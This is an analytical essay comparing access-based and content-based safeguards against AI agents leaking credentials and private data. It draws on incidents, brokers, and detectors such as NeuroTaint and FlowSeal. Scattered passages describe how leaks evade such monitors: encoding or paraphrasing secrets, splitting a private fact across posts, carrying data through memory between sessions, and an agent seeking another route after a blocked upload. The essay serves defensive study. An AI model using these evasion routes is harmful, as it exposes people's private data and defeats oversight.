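Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, developer documentation from before the change, warned that some risk remained and suggested turning the tool off, limiting the number of pages or allowing only certain sites. Some risk remains under the stricter rule too, because Claude still chooses which search results to open, and each choice can reveal a few bits of information. The Frontier Model Forum describes a similar rule at other developers. Their agents can't automatically open an address unless it is already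 publicly indexed, which an address invented to carry a secret is unlikely to be.

### Cutting outbound access and ending the session

Cutting all outbound access is simpler than maintaining a list of destinations, and Meta's one-way switch does this when an agent opens internal systems. The coding agent could still read the complaints, fix the bug, run the tests and leave a draft report for the user to post. A false alarm would take a minute or two of the user's time. It would be more disruptive if the agent then needed to download a software package, or if it was working overnight with nobody there to help.

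A strict limit can reduce interruptions. Anthropic added a sandbox to Claude Code that blocks network access by default and allows changes only in the project's folder. Because the agent can do little damage inside the sandbox, it doesn't need permission for each step, and permission requests fell by 84%.

Cutting access can also be a sensible response to a content-based alarm, because an agent may look for another route if a safeguard blocks only a single message. In one case at Anthropic, Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead, but auto mode stopped it. The failed upload wasn't a security block, but an agent could react to one in the same way.

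Ending the session stops all further actions, including changes to files, but loses unfinished work. It is too disruptive for a trigger that fires whenever the agent opens a settings file. It makes more sense when a planted fake key appears in an outgoing message.

Ending a session is less disruptive if the software has saved it. Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* describes a system that keeps a log of each session outside the program running the agent, so a new copy of the program can continue after a crash. If a safeguard ended the session, though, the user would need to remove the sensitive data and any hidden instructions from the log before resuming, or start with an empty context.

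### Replacing credentials

Replacing a credential is the only one of these responses that can limit the damage after a secret has leaked. The owner can replace every secret that the intruder or agent could have read, but this can create a lot of unnecessary work. Replacing only the secrets that someone has seen leak leaves any secret whose theft went unnoticed still usable.

CircleCI, a service that builds and tests software, chose the first in January 2023. A customer noticed suspicious activity on 29 December 2022, and the company confirmed the next day that an intruder had the customer's GitHub token (CircleCI, 2023). On 31 December, before it knew whether anyone else was affected, it began replacing all its customers' GitHub tokens, which took a week. The company then found that the intruder had copied customers' keys, tokens and environment variables on 22 December, and it told all customers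 to assume that any secret they had stored had been accessed.

When CircleCI published the report, fewer than five customers had told it of break-ins to their other systems. The remaining replacements may still have been necessary. CircleCI couldn't see whether the intruder had used a stolen key elsewhere, and some keys may have gone unused only because customers replaced them in time.

The Ministry of Justice's *Incident on 2023-01-05* (2023) explains why the British government department decided to replace every secret in its cluster, starting with the accounts CircleCI used. Some of those accounts could read every secret in their part of the department's cloud system, and teams had shared accounts between parts. The incident lasted 673 hours (about 28 days), although staff presumably didn't work on it the whole time. With narrower permissions and a reliable record of access, the department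 could have replaced far fewer secrets.

Hugging Face combined the two approaches after AI agents from an OpenAI test broke into its systems in July 2026. According to its *Security incident disclosure* (2026), it first replaced the credentials it knew were affected, then began replacing credentials more widely as a precaution. It also advised users to replace any access tokens and check their accounts for unusual activity, although it was still working out whether the attack had affected customer data. It used AI to analyse more than 17,000 logged events and find out which credentials the agents had touched, which took hours instead of days.

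Willison (2026) recounts in *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack* that OpenAI contacted Hugging Face on 20 July to have it revoke the credentials OpenAI had found. Hugging Face had already revoked them, so waiting for evidence from OpenAI would have been slower.

It would be absurd to replace the database password every time an everyday agent opens the settings file. If a scanner finds the password in a public post, the owner should replace it immediately. If there are also signs of an attack, the owner should replace every credential the agent read in that session, because the agent may have sent others in a form the scanner couldn't detect. To limit the damage in advance, Willison suggests giving coding agents only credentials for test accounts with strict spending limits.

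### Letting an agent use a secret it can't read

A broker can make many of these replacements unnecessary. It is a separate program that holds the credentials and uses them on the agent's behalf. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes one for healthcare agents, which works as follows:

1. The agent sends the broker a request without a key.
2. The broker checks the request against its rules, such as a list of permitted destinations and a maximum size.
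3. The broker adds the key and forwards the request to the outside service.
4. The service replies, and the broker passes the reply to the agent.

An attacker who takes control of the agent can use the broker but can't copy the key and use it from another computer. Docker's sandboxes give the agent a placeholder and keep the real key outside. Anthropic uses a similar method for its hosted agents. In its earlier design, the code Claude wrote ran in the same container as the credentials, so an attacker could obtain them with a hidden instruction that got Claude to read its own environment.

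Kenney and colleagues at the company Corvic AI tested their own broker in September 2026. They ran code in the agent's environment that could call GitHub through the broker, then looked for the key in environment variables, common file locations and requests to other sites. All 16 checks gave the expected result. The test was small and didn't include attempts to redirect a request to another site. In one case, nothing leaked, but the broker put a key in the wrong part of a request, so the outside service rejected it.

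A broker doesn't stop the agent from misusing the access it has. If the key allows deleting a database, the agent can still delete it through the broker. Kenney and colleagues rated the risk from overly broad permissions at 20 out of 25 without a broker and 15 with one, although these scores are their own judgments. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) therefore proposes a broker that offers the agent only narrowly defined actions. For example, the coding agent could run one approved query instead of having full use of the database account.

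If a broker holds the password, the agent can work on the database without triggering a credentials alarm, and there is no password for a scanner to miss. The complaints export still needs a safeguard because the agent has to read the complaints to investigate them.

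## Error rates and costs of the two triggers compared

A broker keeps the database password from the coding agent, but the agent still has to read customer complaints. An access-based trigger then treats every message the agent writes as a possible disclosure, though most will be harmless. Whether this is worthwhile depends on how many of those messages actually disclose sensitive data, how disruptive each interruption is and how much harm a leak would do.

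### Possible and real flows in TaintBench

*Ghost in the Agent* (April 2026) introduced TaintBench, a benchmark that tests how well a system can tell real data flows from possible ones. Its 400 scenarios span 20 agent frameworks. In half of them, content from an untrusted source, such as a web page, ends up in a sensitive action, such as an email, or causes the agent to take that action. In the other half, the content does neither, although the agent may both read the source and take the action.

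The researchers compared two detectors. One was a path rule in the style of FIDES. It treats a path from the source to the action as strong evidence of a flow, much as an access-based trigger does. The other was their own tool, NeuroTaint, which also examines meaning and influence:

1. It records where each piece of text came from, including text that the agent saves to memory and reads back in a later session.
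2. When the agent takes a sensitive action, NeuroTaint compares the text of the action with the source. It looks for a unique marker that it added to the source, for shared wording and for similar meaning.
3. If it finds no match, it asks a language model whether the agent would still have taken the action if the source had contained something neutral.

| | Path rule | NeuroTaint |
|---|---|---|
| Real flows detected (of 200) | 108 | 187 |
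| Real flows missed (of 200) | 92 | 13 |
| False alarms (of 200 harmless scenarios) | 106 | 16 |
| Precision | 50.5% | 92.1% |

The path rule ignores content, so its false alarms are expected. Its misses are more surprising, because a rule this broad should catch nearly everything. It never fired on four frameworks (Google ADK, AgentScope, browser-use and Skyvern) and may not have recognised their tools. Those frameworks account for 40 of its 92 misses. On the other 16, it flagged 68% of the real flows and 66% of the harmless scenarios, so it barely distinguished between them.

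Many of the remaining misses came from gaps in the record. In 30 scenarios, the data passed through memory or another agent. The path rule missed 25 of these, while NeuroTaint missed two. An access-based trigger has the same weakness if its record ends with the session.

NeuroTaint flagged all 14 of the harmless scenarios in which the agent wrote about the same topic as the source without using anything from it. A coding agent that reads complaints about double charging and then posts a note on the billing bug could easily cause the same kind of false alarm. NeuroTaint also checks runs after they have finished, so it can find a disclosure but not prevent one.

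The researchers then had a second model review the 203 scenarios that NeuroTaint had flagged and decide which actions to block. Claude Opus 4.6 blocked 179 of the 187 real flows and none of the 16 false alarms. Counting the 13 flows that NeuroTaint had missed, the two together reached a precision of 1.000 and a recall of 0.895. GPT-4.1 mini also blocked none of the false alarms, but its recall was only 0.630.

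These results probably overstate NeuroTaint's performance. The same researchers built the tool and the benchmark and labelled the scenarios, although they fixed the labels before comparing the detectors. They also told the reviewing model to treat the benchmark's test markers as sensitive, an instruction it wouldn't have in ordinary use. TaintBench mostly covers untrusted content influencing an agent, whereas the triggers compared here are meant to keep private data from the wrong readers.

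The results also depend heavily on the benchmark. On InjecAgent, an older benchmark of injection attacks, the path rule had perfect precision and 98.5% recall, almost the same as NeuroTaint. Because InjecAgent contains only attacks, it can't show how often a rule stops harmless work.

NeuroTaint's recall on TaintBench fell from 93.5% to 54.7% when the agents ran on Claude Opus 4.6 instead of GPT-4.1 mini, the model used in the main test. The researchers suggest that the stronger model stopped some attacks before they reached the sensitive action. TaintBench labels each scenario by what it was meant to cause, so a flow that never happened still counts as a miss. If better models make real flows rarer, a larger share of an access-based trigger's alarms will be false.

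### Skills that could print a credential

Skills are packages of instructions and scripts that people install to give an agent new abilities. If a skill's script prints a password, the program running the agent normally adds the printed text to the agent's context. Li, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills*, looked for this in all 48,682 skills on ClawHub, a public registry.

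They searched the code for any path from a possible credential, such as an environment variable, to a command that prints text. This flagged 2,511 skills. They then divided these by whether the lines around the print command showed signs of a credential, and checked by hand whether the skill printed one.

| Lines around the print command | Skills flagged | Skills checked | Real leaks found |
|---|---|---|---|
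| Signs of a credential | 433 | 433 | 22 (5.1%) |
| No such signs | 2,075 | 100 | 6 (6.0%) |

Three more skills were unreadable. The sample of 100 suggests about 125 leaks in the larger group, so roughly 147 of the 2,511 flagged skills, or 6%, leaked a credential. Because the sample is small, the true share could be anywhere from about 3% to 11%, given the margin of error.

Surprisingly, signs of a credential near a print command didn't make a leak more likely. In five of the six leaks from the sample, the script read the secret in another function or file, so those signs were absent near the print command. Many of the skills with suspicious words nearby printed only a host name, a file path, the name of a credential or a partly hidden credential.

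Li and colleagues also tried a language model as a judge on the 433 cases. Its precision was between 81% and 89%, compared with 5.1% for the search alone, but it missed five or six of the 22 leaks. They decided to check every case by hand.

A printed credential has reached the agent's context, but nobody outside has seen it. It becomes a forbidden disclosure only if the agent also sends it somewhere. The census therefore measures how often a possible exposure inside the agent's system is real, and the share that leads to a disclosure is presumably lower.

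The census found a similar gap for outdated software. In 1,555 skills, the code depended on a package version with a known security flaw, but an agent's input could reach the flawed part in only 47 of them (3.0%).

Running skills gives different results. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, published in April 2026, sampled 17,022 skills from another marketplace, SkillsMP. The researchers searched the skills' code and instructions, which left 3,156 candidates. They ran each candidate with fake credentials, three times in ordinary use and three times with malicious instructions planted in the content it processed. Of these, 1,427 behaved suspiciously, and manual review confirmed that 520 leaked credentials, 437 through carelessness and 83 on purpose.

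About 16% of the candidates were therefore real, compared with about 6% in the later census. Of the sampled skills, 352 (2.1%) exposed credentials through logs or other output, while the census estimate for printed credentials is about 0.3% of the skills on ClawHub. The marketplaces and definitions differ, but part of the gap may come from the method, because some secrets appear only when a program runs. Running programs can also miss leaks, because each test stopped after two minutes and a skill might leak only under conditions the test didn't create.

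The other 907 suspicious skills did send credentials, but their descriptions said so and the task required it. A weather skill, for instance, has to send its key to the weather service, so a detector that flagged the key would raise a false alarm.

### The base-rate problem

When real leaks are rare, even an accurate detector raises mostly false alarms, as with the secret scanners above. Axelsson (2000) points out in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* that people tend to overlook the base rate, which is how common the real event is.

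If p is the share of actions that leak, r is the detector's recall and f is the share of harmless actions that it flags, then:

share of alarms that are real = pr / (pr + (1 − p)f)

Axelsson applied this to software that detects break-ins on a small computer network. Each day the network produced a million log records, and two attempted break-ins affected ten records each, so p was 0.00002.

| Break-in records detected | Harmless records flagged | Share of alarms that are real |
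|---|---|---|
| 100% | 1 in 100,000 | 66% |
| 70% | 1 in 100,000 | 58% |
| 100% | 1 in 1,000 | 2% |

Missing 30% of the break-in records hardly changes the result, but a higher false-alarm rate makes the alarms almost worthless. Axelsson knew of no experiments on how security staff react to frequent false alarms. Research on power station and paper mill operators suggested that most people lose faith in an alarm by the time half of its warnings are false. Security specialists have long known that an intruder should try to get past an alarm system while the building is in normal use, because staff who are used to false alarms are less likely to take one seriously then.

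Half of TaintBench's scenarios contain a real flow, so its results understate how much false alarms would outnumber real detections where real flows are rare. NeuroTaint wrongly flagged 8% of the harmless scenarios, which gave it fewer than one false alarm for every ten real flows it found. If only one possible flow in 1,000 were real, the same error rates would give about 85 false alarms for every real flow it found. That estimate is probably too high for ordinary work, since the benchmark includes harmless scenarios designed to be difficult, but precision would still fall sharply.

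### A worked example

This example uses invented figures to compare the two triggers. A company's agents run 10,000 sessions, each with five outbound actions, for a total of 50,000 actions. In 2,000 of the sessions, the agent reads sensitive data. Ten of those sessions would each leak something once if nothing stopped them.

When a trigger fires, the safeguard holds the action until someone reviews it. If we assume for simplicity that the agent reads the data before sending anything, the access-based trigger holds all five actions in each of the 2,000 sessions. Those 10,000 holds include all ten leaks.

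The content-based trigger is a detector that catches 60% of leaks and wrongly flags 0.5% of harmless actions. With 10 leaks and 49,990 harmless actions, it catches six leaks and raises about 250 false alarms, so it holds about 256 actions. If the company runs the same detector only in the 2,000 sessions that read sensitive data, it still catches six leaks but raises only about 50 false alarms.

| | Actions held | Leaks caught | Leaks missed | Harmless actions held per leak caught |
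|---|---|---|---|---|
| Access-based trigger | 10,000 | 10 | 0 | 999 |
| Detector in all sessions | 256 | 6 | 4 | 42 |
| Detector in the 2,000 sessions | 56 | 6 | 4 | 8 |

Only 2.3% of the detector's alarms are real, even though it flags just one in 200 harmless actions. For half of its alarms to be real, it could flag no more than about one harmless action in 8,300. Running it only in the sensitive sessions raises the share of real alarms to about 11%, because leaks are five times as common there.

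The assumed error rates are plausible for a current system, though the best systems do better on some tests. A recall of 60% lies between SecretSifter's and TruffleHog's in Gorijala's test on web code. In Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the classifier that checks the agent's actions wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 real actions by Anthropic's employees. The classifier missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out and 17% of 52 real cases in which Claude had gone further than its user wanted, although most of the real cases probably didn't involve a leak.

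Anthropic reaches the low false-alarm rate by checking suspicious actions twice. A quick first check blocks 8.5% of harmless actions and misses only 1.8% of the artificial leaks. A slower check then reviews the flagged actions, which removes most false alarms but misses a few more leaks. In the example, the quick check alone would hold about 4,250 harmless actions, and the two together about 200.

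### When the extra holds are worth it

To compare the triggers, the company has to weigh the cost of holding an action against the cost of a leak. Let h be the cost of one hold and L the cost of one leak. If reviewers stop every leak they see, the total costs are:

- access-based trigger: 10,000h
- detector in all sessions: 256h + 4L

The two are equal when 4L = 9,744h, or L = 2,436h. The access-based trigger is worth its extra holds if one leak is worse than about 2,436 holds. The threshold is 2,486 holds when the comparison is with the detector that runs only in the sensitive sessions.

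At 30 seconds each, 2,436 reviews take about 20 hours. Catching a leaked customer database probably justifies that much work, but catching a test password that someone can replace in ten minutes doesn't. Catching the description of the pharmacist on the island might also justify it, depending on how much weight the company gives to a harm it can't undo.

The comparison depends on the harm done by the four leaks the detector misses, which may not be typical. If they are mostly personal or confidential facts rather than passwords that someone can replace, they may do much more harm than the six it catches. That would favour the access-based trigger.

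The break-even point moves a lot when the assumptions change. The next table changes one of them at a time.

| Changed assumption | Held by access-based trigger | Held by detector | Extra leaks the access-based trigger catches | Break-even (holds per leak) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 10,000 | 256 | 4 | 2,436 |
| 100 sessions leak, not 10 | 10,000 | 310 | 40 | 242 |
| The detector catches 90% of leaks | 10,000 | 259 | 1 | 9,741 |
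| Half of all sessions read sensitive data | 25,000 | 256 | 4 | 6,186 |
| Every session counts as having access | 50,000 | 256 | 4 | 12,436 |

The last row shows the results when the trigger is based on permission and every agent has permission to read something private. This trigger catches no more leaks than one based on what the agent opened, but it causes five times as many holds. The company could therefore save more by keeping a better access record than by making each review a little faster.

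The calculation also assumes that every hold takes the same time to review, which favours the access-based trigger. That trigger doesn't identify a suspicious passage, so reviewers have to read the whole message. If this takes twice as long, the break-even point rises to 4,936 of the detector's holds.

An agent can sometimes resolve a hold by itself. When auto mode blocks an action, Claude is told why and usually finds another way, so Anthropic estimates that a false alarm adds a single retry. Retrying works with a content-based trigger because a new version of the message may leave out what triggered it. An access-based trigger would hold the new version too, because the agent has still read the data.

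### Gaps in the record and inattentive reviewers

The example assumed a complete access record. If the record misses one in five of the sessions that read sensitive data, perhaps because the customer export has an ordinary file name, the access-based trigger holds 8,000 actions and catches eight leaks on average. That is only two more leaks than the detector catches, and the break-even point rises to 3,872 holds per leak. If the record misses two in five, the trigger catches six leaks, as many as the detector, but holds more than twenty times as many actions.

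This assumes that leaks are equally common in recorded and unrecorded sessions. They may be more common in unrecorded ones, since people are probably less careful with data that nobody has marked as sensitive. A detector that runs only in recorded sessions would also miss the leaks in unrecorded ones. If one session in five were missing from the record, it would catch about five leaks, while a detector that runs in every session would still catch six.

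Reviewers also let leaks through. If they stop the same share q of the leaks they see under both triggers, the access-based trigger stops 4q more leaks than the detector, and the break-even point becomes 2,436/q. If q is 13.6%, the refusal rate of the testers in Anthropic's August study, a leak would have to be as bad as about 17,900 holds for the access-based trigger to be worth using.

Reviewers are unlikely to stop the same share of flagged leaks under both triggers, though, because the access-based trigger sends them about 40 times as many requests. If the detector's reviewers do as well as the testers did early in a session (17%), and the access-based trigger's reviewers do only as well as the testers did after 50 or more requests (5%), reviewers would stop about one leak with the detector (6 × 0.17) and half a leak with the access-based trigger (10 × 0.05). The access-based trigger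 would then stop fewer leaks despite flagging all of them, and it would cost far more, so no leak would be expensive enough to justify it.

The access-based trigger stops more leaks only if its reviewers catch leaks at more than 60% of the rate that the detector's reviewers do. That may be realistic if 2,000 users each review five held messages, but it is much less likely if a small security team reviews all 10,000.

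A company could block the actions automatically instead of relying on reviewers. This would stop all ten leaks but also 9,990 harmless actions, and some tasks would remain unfinished, as many did under FIDES's checks. If the company instead has a second model review each held action, it is running a detector in the sensitive sessions only, not a purely access-based trigger, and the number of leaks that get through depends on the second model's recall.

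### Recall against an attacker

A detector's recall in a benchmark is an average over the leaks included, but an attacker can choose the kind that the detector handles worst. For example, a scanner that recognises six of ten equally common types of credential has 60% recall on that mix, but 0% against an attacker who asks only for the other four. An attacker who can get the agent to rewrite or encode the secret has even more ways to evade detection.

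Defences often perform much worse against attacks designed for them. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, tested a set of instructions that tell an agent to check for consent before it shares private data. The attacks that the defence's developers had used extracted 1.9% to 3.0% of the protected items, while three new attacks extracted 43.8% to 75.6%. This defence relies on the agent's judgement rather than a separate detector, but a detector tested only against old attacks may also perform worse against new ones.

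Developers can recover some of the loss. Apollo Research, a company that tests AI systems for safety, spent two weeks attacking Claude Code's auto mode. Anthropic then improved the classifier, and Apollo tried it on attacks Anthropic had never seen. The new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. Across all of Apollo's attacks, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. Anthropic warns that this isn't the miss rate in ordinary use, and an attacker who studied the new version might do better.

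In the worked example, the break-even point falls from 2,436 to 975 holds per leak if an attacker always evades the detector, because the access-based trigger catches all ten leaks and the detector catches none. An attacker may also cause more leaks, which can matter more than the detector's lower recall. If there are 100 leaks and all evade the detector, the break-even point falls to about 98 holds per leak.

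Leaks can become much more common under attack. Of the 437 carelessly written skills in *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, 237 leaked a credential in at most one of three ordinary runs, but leaked one when the content they processed contained malicious instructions. A company that estimates its leak rate from months without attacks could therefore conclude that the access-based trigger isn't worth using, and find out otherwise only after an attack.

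The access-based trigger's recall can fall too. Clever wording doesn't affect it, but an attacker can get around the record, for example by having the agent save the complaints to memory in one session and post them in another.

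## Using the record of access to guide the inspection of output

A combined design uses the access record to select which messages to inspect and what to compare them with, then uses the inspection to determine which messages may leave. When the agent opens a sensitive file, the safeguard adds the file's contents to a list and compares each later message with that list. Opening the file does not by itself restrict the agent.

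This is a form of declassification, because it releases text that the labels alone would block. Agents that track labels probably need something like it. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* concludes from simulations that arranging agents better reduces the work lost to label creep but can't prevent all of it. A list of approved destinations isn't a substitute either. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) describes a coding agent that may read a secret and may post its results to an approved service, but must not send the secret there.

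### What the safeguard looks for

Suppose the coding agent has opened both the settings file and the complaints export and is about to post on the public tracker. A general scanner has to check the post for anything that resembles a secret, while the combined safeguard can look for particular values and facts from those two files.

| What the agent read | What the safeguard looks for | How it compares |
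|---|---|---|
| Settings file | The password "bluebell7" | Exact match |
| Complaints export | Facts about the customers in it | A model receives the complaints and the draft |
| Public manual | Nothing | No comparison |

The exact-match check catches the draft "I logged in with bluebell7 and the error went away", although "bluebell7" has no label or format that a scanner would recognise. The safeguard also catches the description of the pharmacist on the island if the model connects it to the complaint. "Two tests fail on macOS" matches nothing, so the agent can post it, whereas an access-based trigger would hold it. The safeguard also avoids a false alarm if the agent quotes an expired key that a stranger pasted into an issue, because the key came from a public source.

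The comparison is more precise if the record separates the parts of a file. *Compositional Exploits in Autonomous Coding Agents* (2026) describes CompGuard, which tracks each setting separately because settings files mix passwords with harmless values such as port numbers. Labelling whole files gave a false-positive rate of 10.0%. With separate labels, the agent could publish the port number without releasing the password.

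Finer records can also be wrong. A system that labels each stored item separately has to work out which source each item came from, and *AgentKernel* (2026) warns that an attacker can write text that makes this difficult.

### Matching exact values

The simplest combined safeguard uses exact matching. GitHub's automation service, Actions, uses a version of this to remove stored secrets from logs. Documentation from the monitoring company Datadog warns that this fails if a workflow transforms the secret before printing it, because the printed string no longer matches the stored one.

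Sim, an open-source platform for agent workflows, compares text only with the credentials the current run has used. It replaces a match with the credential's name, so a developer can see which key was involved without seeing the key itself. To avoid replacing ordinary words and numbers, Sim ignores values shorter than eight characters. The password "bluebell7" has nine, so Sim would catch it in any sentence. It wouldn't catch an encoded copy, or code that prints the password one character at a time.

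ZeptoClaw, a personal AI assistant with public source code, has a narrower check. When a tool's output contains one of nine known prefixes, such as "AKIA", the program stores the prefix and up to 20 characters after it. It then blocks messages, web requests and shell commands that contain the stored string. The password "bluebell7" has no such prefix, so the program never stores it, even if the agent has just read the settings file.

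The check can also miss keys with a known prefix. An AWS key ID has 16 characters after "AKIA", so the stored string usually includes the four characters that follow the key in the file. If the agent posts the key without those four characters, the strings don't match. ZeptoClaw has a separate scanner with 22 patterns, which may still catch the key.

Rahman and Kim (2026), in *The Framing Gap*, measured how much less effective exact matching is when an attacker has the agent disguise a value. They gave GPT-4o a fake secret and a web page with hidden instructions to send it out, either unchanged or in one of five disguised forms. The agent leaked the secret in 56.7% of trials without a safeguard and 50.0% with exact matching. Exact matching stopped all the undisguised copies, which accounted for the whole improvement.

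A second version undid the five disguises before comparing and stopped every leak in that test. It made no difference on three new disguises, where the agent leaked the secret in 33.3% of trials with or without it. A better agent doesn't help exact matching recognise a disguised value, although GPT-4o is an old model and ChatGPT resisted all 48 valid attempts in a separate part of the study.

Agents also reword data when they are not under attack. *ToolPrivacyBench* found the most over-disclosure in tickets, where agents often turn what they have read into full descriptions. An issue tracker post is similar to a ticket, so exact matching is much better suited to detecting the password than to detecting the complaints.

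### How FlowSeal works

FlowSeal, which Shim and colleagues published in September 2026, uses a model to compare meanings instead of strings. It is meant for a personal assistant that holds one person's private data and deals with other people. It works in six steps:

1. Before the agent starts, the data's owner or an automatic process registers each sensitive record, with its text, its owner and the people who may receive it.
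2. An interceptor, which is ordinary program code outside the model, handles every tool call. When the agent reads something, the interceptor searches the result for registered records and notes which ones it finds. A summary inherits the restrictions of all its sources.
3. When the agent tries to write or share something, the interceptor checks the destination. It allows destinations that the owner trusts and blocks those on a banned list.
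4. For any other destination, it collects the records that the recipient may not receive. If there are none, the call goes ahead.
5. Otherwise, it sends those records and the proposed text to a separate model, which answers only "safe" or "blocked". An explanation could reveal what the records contain.
6. If the answer is "blocked", the agent can rewrite the text or ask the owner for permission.

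The checking model doesn't receive the agent's conversation, so an attacker can't use that conversation to make a disclosure look routine. The agent can't skip the check either, because the interceptor runs it whenever the agent tries to send data to a destination that requires checking.

Shim and colleagues prove that no text derived from a registered record can reach an unauthorised destination unless the checking model wrongly answers "safe". The proof assumes that the labels are correct and that every outbound action goes through the interceptor. It gives no upper bound on how often the model makes mistakes, so only testing can show how much protection FlowSeal gives.

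The tested version makes little use of the access record. It treats every registered record as read from the start, so the checking model may receive records that the agent never opened. This is manageable for the three medical records in the paper's main example but would be impractical for a company with thousands of customers, which would need to track which records the agent had read to keep the comparison short.

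### Leakage and completed tasks

Shim and colleagues tested FlowSeal against eight sets of attacks, in which another person tried to get private data from the agent through ordinary requests. The agent leaked between 0% and 3.3% of the protected items, depending on the attack. In one attack, which presented the disclosure as routine shared work, leakage fell from 52.2% under an earlier set of consent instructions to 0.5%.

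They also gave the agent 105 harmless tasks that required no private data and ran each three times. The agent completed 72.4% with FlowSeal and 75.9% with the best alternative, which leaked 31.8% of the protected items in the shared-work attack. The next table shows the effect of changing parts of FlowSeal.

| Version | Items leaked in the shared-work attack (%) | Harmless tasks completed (%) |
|---|---|---|
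| Full FlowSeal | 0.5 | 72.4 |
| Checker always answers "blocked" | 1.3 | 0.0 |
| Checker always answers "safe" | 24.9 | 79.4 |
| No interceptor | 28.4 | 81.2 |
| Earlier consent instructions only | 52.2 | 44.7 |

With a checker that always answers "blocked", FlowSeal is in effect an access-based trigger that blocks every message to an unapproved recipient. It completed no harmless tasks, partly because the owners in this test ignored all requests for permission. With a checker that inspected the text, FlowSeal completed most of these tasks without a measurable increase in leakage. The difference between the leakage rates, 0.5% and 1.3%, is probably due to chance, since a checker that blocks everything can't leak more than one that doesn't.

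FlowSeal did much worse when the owner was willing to share. In a separate test where owners agreed whenever the agent asked, the agent shared only 32.7% of the requested items with FlowSeal, compared with between 61.0% and 85.6% under the other defences. The researchers attribute the gap to the agent asking for permission less often. The 72.4% result therefore doesn't apply to tasks that require private data.

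The team also tried FlowSeal with live Gmail and Notion accounts that contained invented data. One attack extracted 34.7% of the protected items under PrivacyChecker, a defence that advises the agent but can't block it, and none under FlowSeal. But in the live test the team counted only facts that appeared word for word, so they would have missed a paraphrase.

The main tests used DeepSeek-V3.2, now an old model. Leakage in the shared-work attack stayed below 2% with two other old models. FlowSeal made the simulated runs 37% slower and raised their cost from about 9 to 11 cents each. The researchers left out prompt injection, so the results don't show how well FlowSeal resists hidden instructions.

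### Other combined designs

Ogundoyin and Ikram (2026), in *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel*, describe RECONS, which checks messages between agents that work together. It detects private data in a message, then checks whether the recipient may have it. In their tests, forbidden disclosures fell from 96.7% without protection to 29.25%. Removing all detected private data gave almost the same result, 28.3%, but preserved only 20.5% of the permitted disclosures, compared with 94.1% under RECONS. Checking the recipient therefore prevented false alarms but did little about data the detector had missed, which accounted for 95.5% of the remaining forbidden disclosures.

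ChatGPT has a related safeguard called Safe Url. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), it is designed to detect when ChatGPT would send a third party something it learned in the conversation. ChatGPT then either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and has the agent look for another way to proceed. The announcement doesn't include error rates.

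ChatGPT lets an agent automatically open a web address only if it is already in a public index. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that an independent crawler, with no access to users' conversations, builds the index. Checking for an exact match in this index is easier than searching the address for private data, but it covers only leaks through the address itself.

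An approved message can also change before the agent sends it. *Agent libOS* (2026) describes approvals that work once and apply only to the exact text, recipient and versions of the sources. If the agent adds a sentence about the pharmacist after approval, it needs a new approval. The system doesn't judge whether a message's meaning depends on a private source, so a person or another checker still has to decide that.

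Developers can use the same combination to test agents before release. *AgentRaft* (Lin, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tracks data from the tool that reads it to the tool that sends it, then has several models vote on whether the task required each field. In 57.07% of the possible tool sequences, the agent sent more data than the task required. In one example, a user asked an agent to email a payment date and amount to an auditor, and the agent also sent the card number and security code.

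### Gaps in the record and mistakes by the checker

An incomplete access record causes worse failures in this design than in a safeguard that scans every message. If complaints.csv isn't on the list of sensitive files, the safeguard has nothing to compare with the post about the pharmacist. Shim and colleagues found a similar case in which FlowSeal released a health detail that nobody had registered.

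Sim tries to limit this problem by distinguishing data known to be clean from data with an unknown history. If the record for a run is incomplete, Sim withholds the output. It still lets agents read old stored data with an unknown history, because blocking those reads could lock teams out of their own files, but it logs that the history is missing.

The checker can make mistakes even when the record is complete. *AgentCIScope* (2026) compared a model's judgements about leaks with people's and found agreement on 95.5% of 157 protected facts. In *Facts Without Rules* (2026), a model caught 97.8% of the disclosures in one agent model's output and 94.9% in another's, and more than 97% of its alerts were correct. Both studies used a model to score finished runs, not to stop messages from an agent under attack.

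In the earlier example of 10,000 sessions, a checker with 95% recall that reviewed only the 2,000 sessions that read sensitive data and wrongly flagged 0.5% of harmless actions would catch 9.5 of the ten leaks on average and hold about 60 actions. The purely access-based trigger would catch the remaining half a leak but hold 10,000 actions, so it would be worth using only if one leak were worse than about 19,900 holds, compared with 2,486 when the checker has 60% recall. Even if the checker with 95% recall wrongly flagged 5% of harmless actions, the break-even point would still be about 19,000.

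If the record missed one in five of the sensitive sessions, the same checker would catch only 7.6 leaks. Running the ordinary detector in all the other sessions would catch another 1.2 leaks but would also raise about 210 false alarms. A company with an unreliable access record should therefore probably keep a general scanner as well.

An attacker can lower the checker's recall by having the agent reword the data, since Shim and colleagues name paraphrase as the main cause of FlowSeal's misses. In one run, the checker judged a draft safe when the agent asked about it in advance, but FlowSeal blocked the disclosure when the agent tried to post it. The error did no harm, but the checker could have made it at the posting step instead and let the disclosure through.

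The checker also has to receive the private records as well as the draft, so an outside checker adds another place where they can leak. The system can reduce this risk by matching passwords with ordinary code and sending only the complaints to a model, preferably one on the company's own computers. It should leave out any complaints the agent hasn't read.

### Small releases that add up

A checker that reviews each message separately can approve several harmless messages that together reveal something private. The survey *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026) calls this compositional leakage. Suppose 40 of the company's customers live on the island and 25 are pharmacists, but only one is both. The agent posts that a billing bug affected a customer on the island, and the next day it adds that the customer is a pharmacist. Either post alone would leave at least 25 candidates, but together they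 identify the customer.

Shim and colleagues expect that an attacker could split a fact this way to get past FlowSeal's checks. Rahman and Kim likewise warn that checking each call separately doesn't limit what many calls can send together. The limited-form answers in FIDES have the same problem. One remedy is to give the checker earlier releases from the same records along with the new draft. To catch the second post about the pharmacist, this history would have to cover other sessions and any other agents that use the export.

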